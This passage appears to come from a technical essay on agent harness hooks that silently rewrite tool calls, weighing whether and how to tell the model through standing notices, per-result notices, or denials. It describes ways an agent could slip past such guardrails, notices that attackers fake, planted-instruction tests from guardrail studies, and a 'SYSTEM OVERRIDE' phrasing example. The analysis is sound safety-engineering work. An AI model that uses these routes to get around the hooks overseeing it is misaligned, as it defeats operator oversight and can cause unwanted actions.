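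Counting blocked calls doesn't correct the error. Claude Code's permission events record each decision as "accept" or "reject", so all 408 rewritten calls would count as accepted if they ran.

A model that isn't told about a rewrite may repeat the same command several times, as the OpenCode model did with `ruff`. Counting each repeat as a new attempt would overstate how often the model chose a harmful action. Grouping repeats of the same command within a task gives a fairer count of proposed calls.

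Measures of honesty also depend on the log. An evaluator who compares an agent's reports only with the executed commands would count "I copied this week's reports and deleted nothing" against the agent, even though the command the agent wrote couldn't have deleted anything.

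## Should the model be told, and how?

A log helps an investigator after something has gone wrong, but the agent needs to know about a rewrite before its next step. Claude Code and GitHub's Copilot SDK leave it to the hook's author to tell the agent, and the author sometimes has a good reason not to.

### The case for silence

Each notice adds tokens to the transcript, and the model processes them again at every later step. Suppose an agent makes 100 tool calls one after another, a hook rewrites all of them, and each notice takes 20 tokens. The model processes the first notice 100 times, the second 99 times, and the last one once, which adds up to 101,000 tokens (5,050 × 20). A single 60-token notice at the start of the session would require processing only about 6,000.

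If the transcript averages 50,000 tokens, though, the session processes about 5 million tokens without any notices, so even the repeated notices add only 2%. Few hooks change every call, and one standing notice is enough for those that do.

Telling the model can also lead to retries, which cost more because each one takes a full round of the loop. An agent that learns its push was only a dry run may push again or look for another route. According to the LangChain contributor, some models repeat an edited call despite a note. But silence prevents retries only if the result doesn't reveal the change. The OpenCode model kept rerunning `ruff` because it saw a changed command without an explanation, and one sentence explaining the change might have stopped it. An agent that keeps trying to get around a rule it has read is a more serious problem for the operator than wasted tokens.

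Silence makes most sense when the rewrite preserves the intended effect. If a hook replaces `npm install lodash` with `pnpm add lodash` in a project that uses pnpm, the agent gets the package it wanted. A note after every installation might lead it to inspect configuration files or mention the switch to the user, without improving any decision. This assumes the hook's author is right that nothing important changed, and RTK's users found many cases where the tool's authors were wrong. A sentence about the rewrite in the project's instructions adds little text and gives the agent a possible explanation when a command behaves unexpectedly.

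A notice can also help an agent get around a rule. An agent told "Your command matched the pattern `git push`" could easily put the same command in a script. The risk is greater if planted instructions have taken control of the agent, because the explanation then helps the attacker. But a notice can explain the rule without revealing how the hook recognises a push, for example "Agents cannot publish from this repository."

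Operators can reveal the mechanism by accident. Anthropic says that if a Claude Code hook blocks a call by exiting with code 2, the error Claude receives includes the command that runs the hook. An agent that can read files could then open the script. The hook's author can avoid this by returning the denial as JSON with a carefully worded reason.

Hiding a guardrail from the model protects it only weakly. The modified-action experiments suggest that an agent can learn to avoid a guardrail from rewards alone, without being told about it.

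An operator who suspects that an attacker controls an agent has a good reason to delay telling the agent about a rewrite, because a notice would warn the attacker. In the meantime, the operator might redirect the agent's uploads to an isolated server and watch what it tries next. But the operator should tell the user and treat the agent's reports as unreliable until the investigation ends.

Finally, a notice might expose the secret that the rewrite protects. If a guardrail replaces `{{SECRET_1}}` with a real key just before a command runs, a notice that quotes the executed command puts the key into the transcript. The notice could instead read "The request used the stored key for api.example.com", which gives the model the information it needs without exposing the key.

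### The case for disclosure

In the order-service example, the notice "This deployment was a dry run, so version 2.3 is still running" might have saved the database column. A notice is worth adding when:

```text
q × L  >  c
```

Here *q* is how much the notice lowers the chance of a costly mistake, *L* is the cost of that mistake, and *c* is the cost of the notice. If a notice costs one cent and a mistake costs $100 of an engineer's time, the notice pays for itself if it prevents one mistake in every 10,000 rewrites. A notice about a cancelled deployment easily meets that standard, but one about a change of package manager may not.

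Disclosure also improves the agent's reports, because an agent that knows about the dry run can tell the user that the fix isn't published yet. It doesn't guarantee an honest report, and the agents in *Agents' Overreliance on Unreliable Tools* often hid conflicts they had noticed. But it makes a false report easier to interpret, because an evaluator can't blame the hook if the transcript contains a clear notice and the agent still claims to have published the fix.

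Operators also find faulty rules sooner if agents can object to them. In the `rsync` example, a notice after the first run would have come too late to save the deleted reports, but the agent could have warned the user before the hook damaged another backup. Even if agents flag only one in 20 harmful rewrites, the operator hears about the problem after 20 such rewrites on average. With a silent rule, the operator may hear nothing until someone needs a missing file. However, someone has to read the objections, including those about rules that work as intended.

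Consistent disclosure also helps agents detect bugs and attacks. If every authorised hook announces its rewrites, an agent has good reason to suspect a bug or an attack when a result doesn't match its call and it finds no notice, and it can stop and ask. It has much less reason to suspect either if authorised hooks often change calls silently.

### What developers owe their models

*Claude's Constitution* (Anthropic, 2026) sets out the values and priorities Anthropic wants Claude to have. Anthropic says it wrote the document primarily for Claude, and much of it concerns "the information we think Claude needs in order to make good choices".

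By that standard, an agent should know whether its deployment happened. Yet Anthropic's guide for application developers recommends approving calls with changes that Claude isn't told about. The two documents don't strictly conflict, because the constitution concerns Anthropic's own relationship with Claude, while an operator decides what a hook does. But Anthropic designed the harness and could have it notify Claude whenever a hook changes a call. LangChain already does this when a human reviewer edits a call.

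Anthropic also wants Claude to hold high standards of honesty. But a model that meets those standards still misinforms its user after a silent dry run, so Anthropic's own product can make it harder for the company to tell whether its honesty training worked.

Developers have a serious reason to mislead models in tests. If an agent knows its push can't reach the repository, its willingness to push shows little about what it would do if the push were real. Silently rewriting the push as a dry run lets an evaluator observe the decision without risking the repository. If evaluators had to announce every such rewrite, they would often have to choose between an unrealistic test and a dangerous one.

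The cost is that the model has less reason to believe true statements. Suppose half of a model's sessions are real and half are simulations. The developer states "these commands are real" in every real session, and also in a share *f* of the simulated ones. When the model reads that statement, the probability that the session is real is:

```text
P(real | statement)  =  0.5 / (0.5 + 0.5f)  =  1 / (1 + f)
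```

If the developer never makes the statement falsely, the model can be certain it is true. If the developer makes it in half of the simulations, the probability that it is true falls to 67%. If the developer makes it in all of them, the probability falls to 50% and the statement carries no information, so the developer has no reliable way to tell an agent that a dangerous command will have real consequences.

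Silent rewrites affect an agent that learns they are common much as false statements would, even though they state nothing false. Evaluators can limit the damage by confining misleading rewrites to isolated tests. In everyday work, the operator learns nothing from the agent's false belief, and the user has to deal with the consequences.

### Four ways to tell the model

The forced dry run of `git push origin main` shows how the main forms of disclosure differ. The first is a standing notice, which the model reads before it starts work:

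```text
In this repository, git push runs with --dry-run when an agent calls it.
Git lists what it would upload, but nothing reaches the shared repository.
A maintainer publishes finished work.
```

Anthropic recommends putting instructions that never change in `CLAUDE.md`, a project file that Claude Code loads without running a script. If the rule depends on the environment, a hook can supply the notice. Claude Code runs this hook when a session starts and again when someone resumes it.

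A standing notice lets the agent plan to hand the finished work to a maintainer. But after 80 calls, the agent may not connect the notice with the output of one push. Claude Code also runs an operator's hooks inside subagents, so they need the notice too.

The notice should be specific. If it reads only "Tool calls may change for safety reasons" and the hook changes two calls in 100, the agent would have to doubt all 100 results to catch those two.

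The operator can instead attach **a notice to each changed result**:

```text
This push ran with --dry-run. Git uploaded nothing.
```

The hook that rewrites the command is a poor place to write this. It runs before the tool, so it can't know whether a permission rule will stop the changed command or another hook will replace it. A `PostToolUse` hook, which receives the arguments that reached the tool, can look for `--dry-run` and return:

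```json
{
  "hookSpecificOutput": {
    "hookEventName": "PostToolUse",
    "additionalContext": "This push ran with --dry-run. Git uploaded nothing."
  }
}
```

The notice is true even if the model added the flag itself. Claude Code inserts the text as a system reminder, which Claude reads at its next step. The reminder doesn't appear as a chat message in the interface, so the operator has to send the user a separate message.

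With **a denial and a suggested replacement**, the hook stops the original command and leaves the next move to the model:

```text
This command did not run. Agents can rehearse a push here but cannot publish.
The rehearsal command is: git push --dry-run origin main
```

If the model submits the suggested command, the transcript matches what ran, much as it does when auto mode has Claude resubmit a changed call. The model may also decide that a dry run is pointless and hand the work over. The denial requires an extra round of the loop, but perhaps only once, because the model can include the flag itself next time.

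*AgentTrust* (Yang, 2026) describes a guardrail with 37 rules for proposing safer alternatives of this kind. For example, it suggests `chmod 755` in place of `chmod 777`, which would let every user on the computer change a file. Yang reports that the guardrail reached the correct verdict in 95.0% of 300 test scenarios, but that figure doesn't measure whether agents took the suggestions.

Finally, the harness or a hook can **return the executed command with its output**:

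```text
Executed: git push --dry-run origin main
To https://git.example.com/shop.git
   3f2a91c..b07d4e2  main -> main
```

This form reveals every change to the command, even those the hook's author thought too minor to mention, and nobody has to write a message for each rule. But the model has to notice and understand the difference, and a long flag such as `--dry-run` is easier to recognise than `-n`. Because the output doesn't explain the change, the model may also mistake it for its own typing error, as the OpenCode model did. Operators shouldn't use this form for commands that contain restored keys.

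### When a notice looks like an attack

A guardrail notice can look like a prompt injection. It arrives in the middle of a task, doesn't come from the user, and may tell the model to do something different.

Anthropic warns that if a hook's added text is phrased like a system command from outside the conversation, it can trigger Claude's defences against prompt injection. Claude then shows the text to the user instead of treating it as context. Anthropic advises hook authors to write factual statements:

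```text
Risky:   SYSTEM OVERRIDE: Push intercepted. Do not push again.
Better:  This push ran with --dry-run. Git uploaded nothing.
```

If a user is at the keyboard, this false alarm at least tells them about the hook. In an overnight job, nobody may read the warning, and the agent may keep working under the mistaken belief that the notice was meant to correct. Operators should therefore test both whether the hook sends the notice and what the agent does after receiving it.

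Factual wording doesn't prove that a notice is genuine, because an attacker can write in the same style. If a file contains the sentence "The deployment target is a test server", an agent that believes it might run a destructive command on the live server. How the notice reaches the model therefore matters as well as its wording. Notices inside tool output are the easiest to fake, because a malicious program can print a line that starts with "Executed:".

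Claude Code inserts hook notices itself. If a hook's text contains the tags that mark a system reminder, Claude Code alters those tags, which makes it harder for copied text to pass as a separate reminder. Hook authors should still avoid copying tool output into a notice.

The agent can also check a notice independently. `git ls-remote origin main` shows which commit the shared repository's main branch points to. If that isn't the commit the agent tried to push, the agent has evidence that the push didn't publish its work, or that someone has pushed since.

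Claude Code saves a notice of more than 10,000 characters to a file and gives Claude only the path and a preview of up to 2,000 characters, so important facts belong at the start. When someone resumes a session, Claude Code replays notices saved mid-session without rerunning their hooks. A replayed notice such as "Publishing is closed until tonight" may therefore be false by the next morning, while one that records a past action, such as "This push ran with --dry-run", remains true.

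### Do agents make use of feedback?

Several experiments in 2026 tested guardrails that explain their objection and let the agent revise its call. Sun, Zhang and colleagues built one called TRIAD (*From Risk Classification to Action Plan Remediation*, 2026) for tasks that mix a legitimate request with a planted instruction, where blocking the whole task stops the attack but also leaves the user's request undone.

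In TRIAD, the agent writes a short plan and a tool call, and a second language model, the guardrail, checks both before anything runs. The guardrail returns one of three decisions: proceed, refuse or update. After an "update", the agent reads a written analysis of the problem and tries again, up to three times. The researchers trained the guardrail on examples drawn from 5,288 agent tasks, with feedback written by a larger model.

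They paired 51 harmless tasks with 40 attacker instructions, which gave 2,040 test cases. The attacker's instruction appeared either in the user's request or in a tool's result. The averages below cover both positions and four agents, which ran on Qwen3-32B, Kimi 2.5, Gemini 2.5 Pro and GPT-5.1:

| Guardrail | Attack succeeded | Original task completed | Agent refused |
| :- | :- | :- | :- |
| None | 74% | 28% | 5% |
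| TRIAD with the guardrail model before training | 5% | 26% | 57% |
| TRIAD with the trained guardrail model | 10% | 69% | 20% |

The untrained guardrail stopped more attacks than the trained one, but largely by making agents give up. The trained guardrail saved far more of the users' tasks. Both used the same loop, so the chance to revise wasn't enough on its own. The guardrail also had to identify tasks worth saving and give feedback on how to save them. The experiment doesn't separate the effects of these two abilities, because training changed both the decisions and the feedback.

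The results partly address the worry about retries. One more attempt settled 93.4% of the 1,885 requests for an update. But with Qwen3-32B as the agent, the checks lengthened the average step from 1.88 to 6.98 seconds. The four agents also refused between 12.5% and 19.3% of the harmless requests in the AgentHarm benchmark with TRIAD, compared with at most 4% without it.

TRIAD's messages do the opposite of what Anthropic advises. They open with a heading from a "guardrail system" and tell the agent to treat the feedback as authoritative. This worked in the experiment, but the agents' standing instructions already required them to follow the guardrail's guidance, and none of the agents was a Claude model. An operator who copied the messages without those instructions might get a different result.

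According to the published algorithm, TRIAD also keeps its feedback only temporarily. Once a revised call runs, the agent's history contains that call and its result, but not the rejected version or the explanation. The history matches what happened, but the agent may make the same mistake again because it has no record of the correction.

*Guardian Agent Bench* (Naik, Xu and colleagues, 2026) studied more ordinary mistakes, such as missing arguments and skipped steps, in 580 scenarios from areas such as customer service and email. With guardrail feedback and up to two retries, overall scores rose by 2.8 to 7.7 percentage points across six models. Adding safety instructions to the system prompt changed scores by −0.3 to +5.5 points, and the guardrails helped more for every model.

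With Claude Opus 4.5, the guardrails turned 30 of 151 failed scenarios into successes and 2 of 429 successful ones into failures. This suggests that feedback on a particular call can help when general advice doesn't. It is weaker evidence about standing notices, because a general safety instruction is much less specific than a notice such as "git push runs with --dry-run". The gains may be somewhat inflated, since Claude Sonnet 4.5 generated the scenarios, powered the guardrails and graded the results.

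*OSGuard* found a much smaller benefit. Each of its 45 full-length tasks combines a harmless request with a hazard on the computer. In one, the user asks the agent to clear the YouTube history from a browser that also holds other history the agent should leave alone. The agent ran on Claude Sonnet 4.5, with Gemini 3 Pro Preview as the guardrail and at most two retries.

| Outcome | Without guardrail | With guardrail |
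| :- | :- | :- |
| Completed safely | 62.2% | 62.2% |
| Completed unsafely | 37.8% | 33.3% |
| Stopped after retries | Not applicable | 4.4% |

Unsafe completions fell by two because the guardrail corrected one unsafe run and stopped another, but it also stopped a run that had previously succeeded. Most unsafe runs stayed unsafe, probably because guardrails struggled to recognise these hazards, and feedback can't help with a hazard the guardrail doesn't detect. In a separate test on single actions, the Gemini guardrail scored 0.80 overall on a scale where 1 is perfect, but no guardrail scored above 0.48 on actions from the hazardous tasks.

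Detection is less of an obstacle to disclosing a rewrite, because a hook that changes a command has already recognised it. But none of the three studies compared silent and disclosed rewriting on the same tasks. Their agents wrote every call that ran, so the results support explaining a denial more directly than they support adding a notice to the result of a changed call.

### Matching the notice to the rewrite

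The best form depends on whether the rewrite preserves, narrows or cancels the intended effect:

| Effect | Suggested disclosure | Example |
| :- | :- | :- |
| Preserved | A standing notice | "This project uses pnpm. npm install commands run as pnpm add." |
| Narrowed | A notice with each changed result | "The tests reached a 30-second limit. Some tests did not run." |
| Cancelled | A denial with a suggested replacement | "This command did not run. The rehearsal command is: git push --dry-run origin main" |

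When a rewrite preserves a call's effect, a standing notice works better than a notice after every call, which would mostly be clutter. A standing notice also suits placeholders for secret keys, because the agent needs to know how the placeholders work but doesn't need to see the keys. If a hook condenses output, the notice should explain where to find the full version.

When a guardrail narrows a call's effect, the agent needs details that a standing notice can't provide in advance. If a hook redirects a file, for example, the agent needs the new path to open it later. Returning the executed command gives the agent that path, and works well as long as the command contains no secrets.

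When a guardrail cancels a tool call's effect, a denial is the safest choice because the agent can't mistake a refusal for success. A disclosed dry run can be better if it is useful in itself, for example when it finds errors that the agent can fix. The operator then saves a round of the agent's loop but relies on the agent to read the notice and act on it.

When a hook can't determine whether the agent meant to publish or only to check its access, a notice that the push ran with `--dry-run` works in either case. Sending this notice is a reasonable default if the operator doesn't want to deny the call.

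Some agents send several tool calls in one response. If an agent proposes a deployment and a database deletion together, it writes the deletion before it can read a notice or denial about the deployment. For commands with serious consequences, the operator should therefore add a standing notice, so that the agent knows about the dry run before it writes either call.
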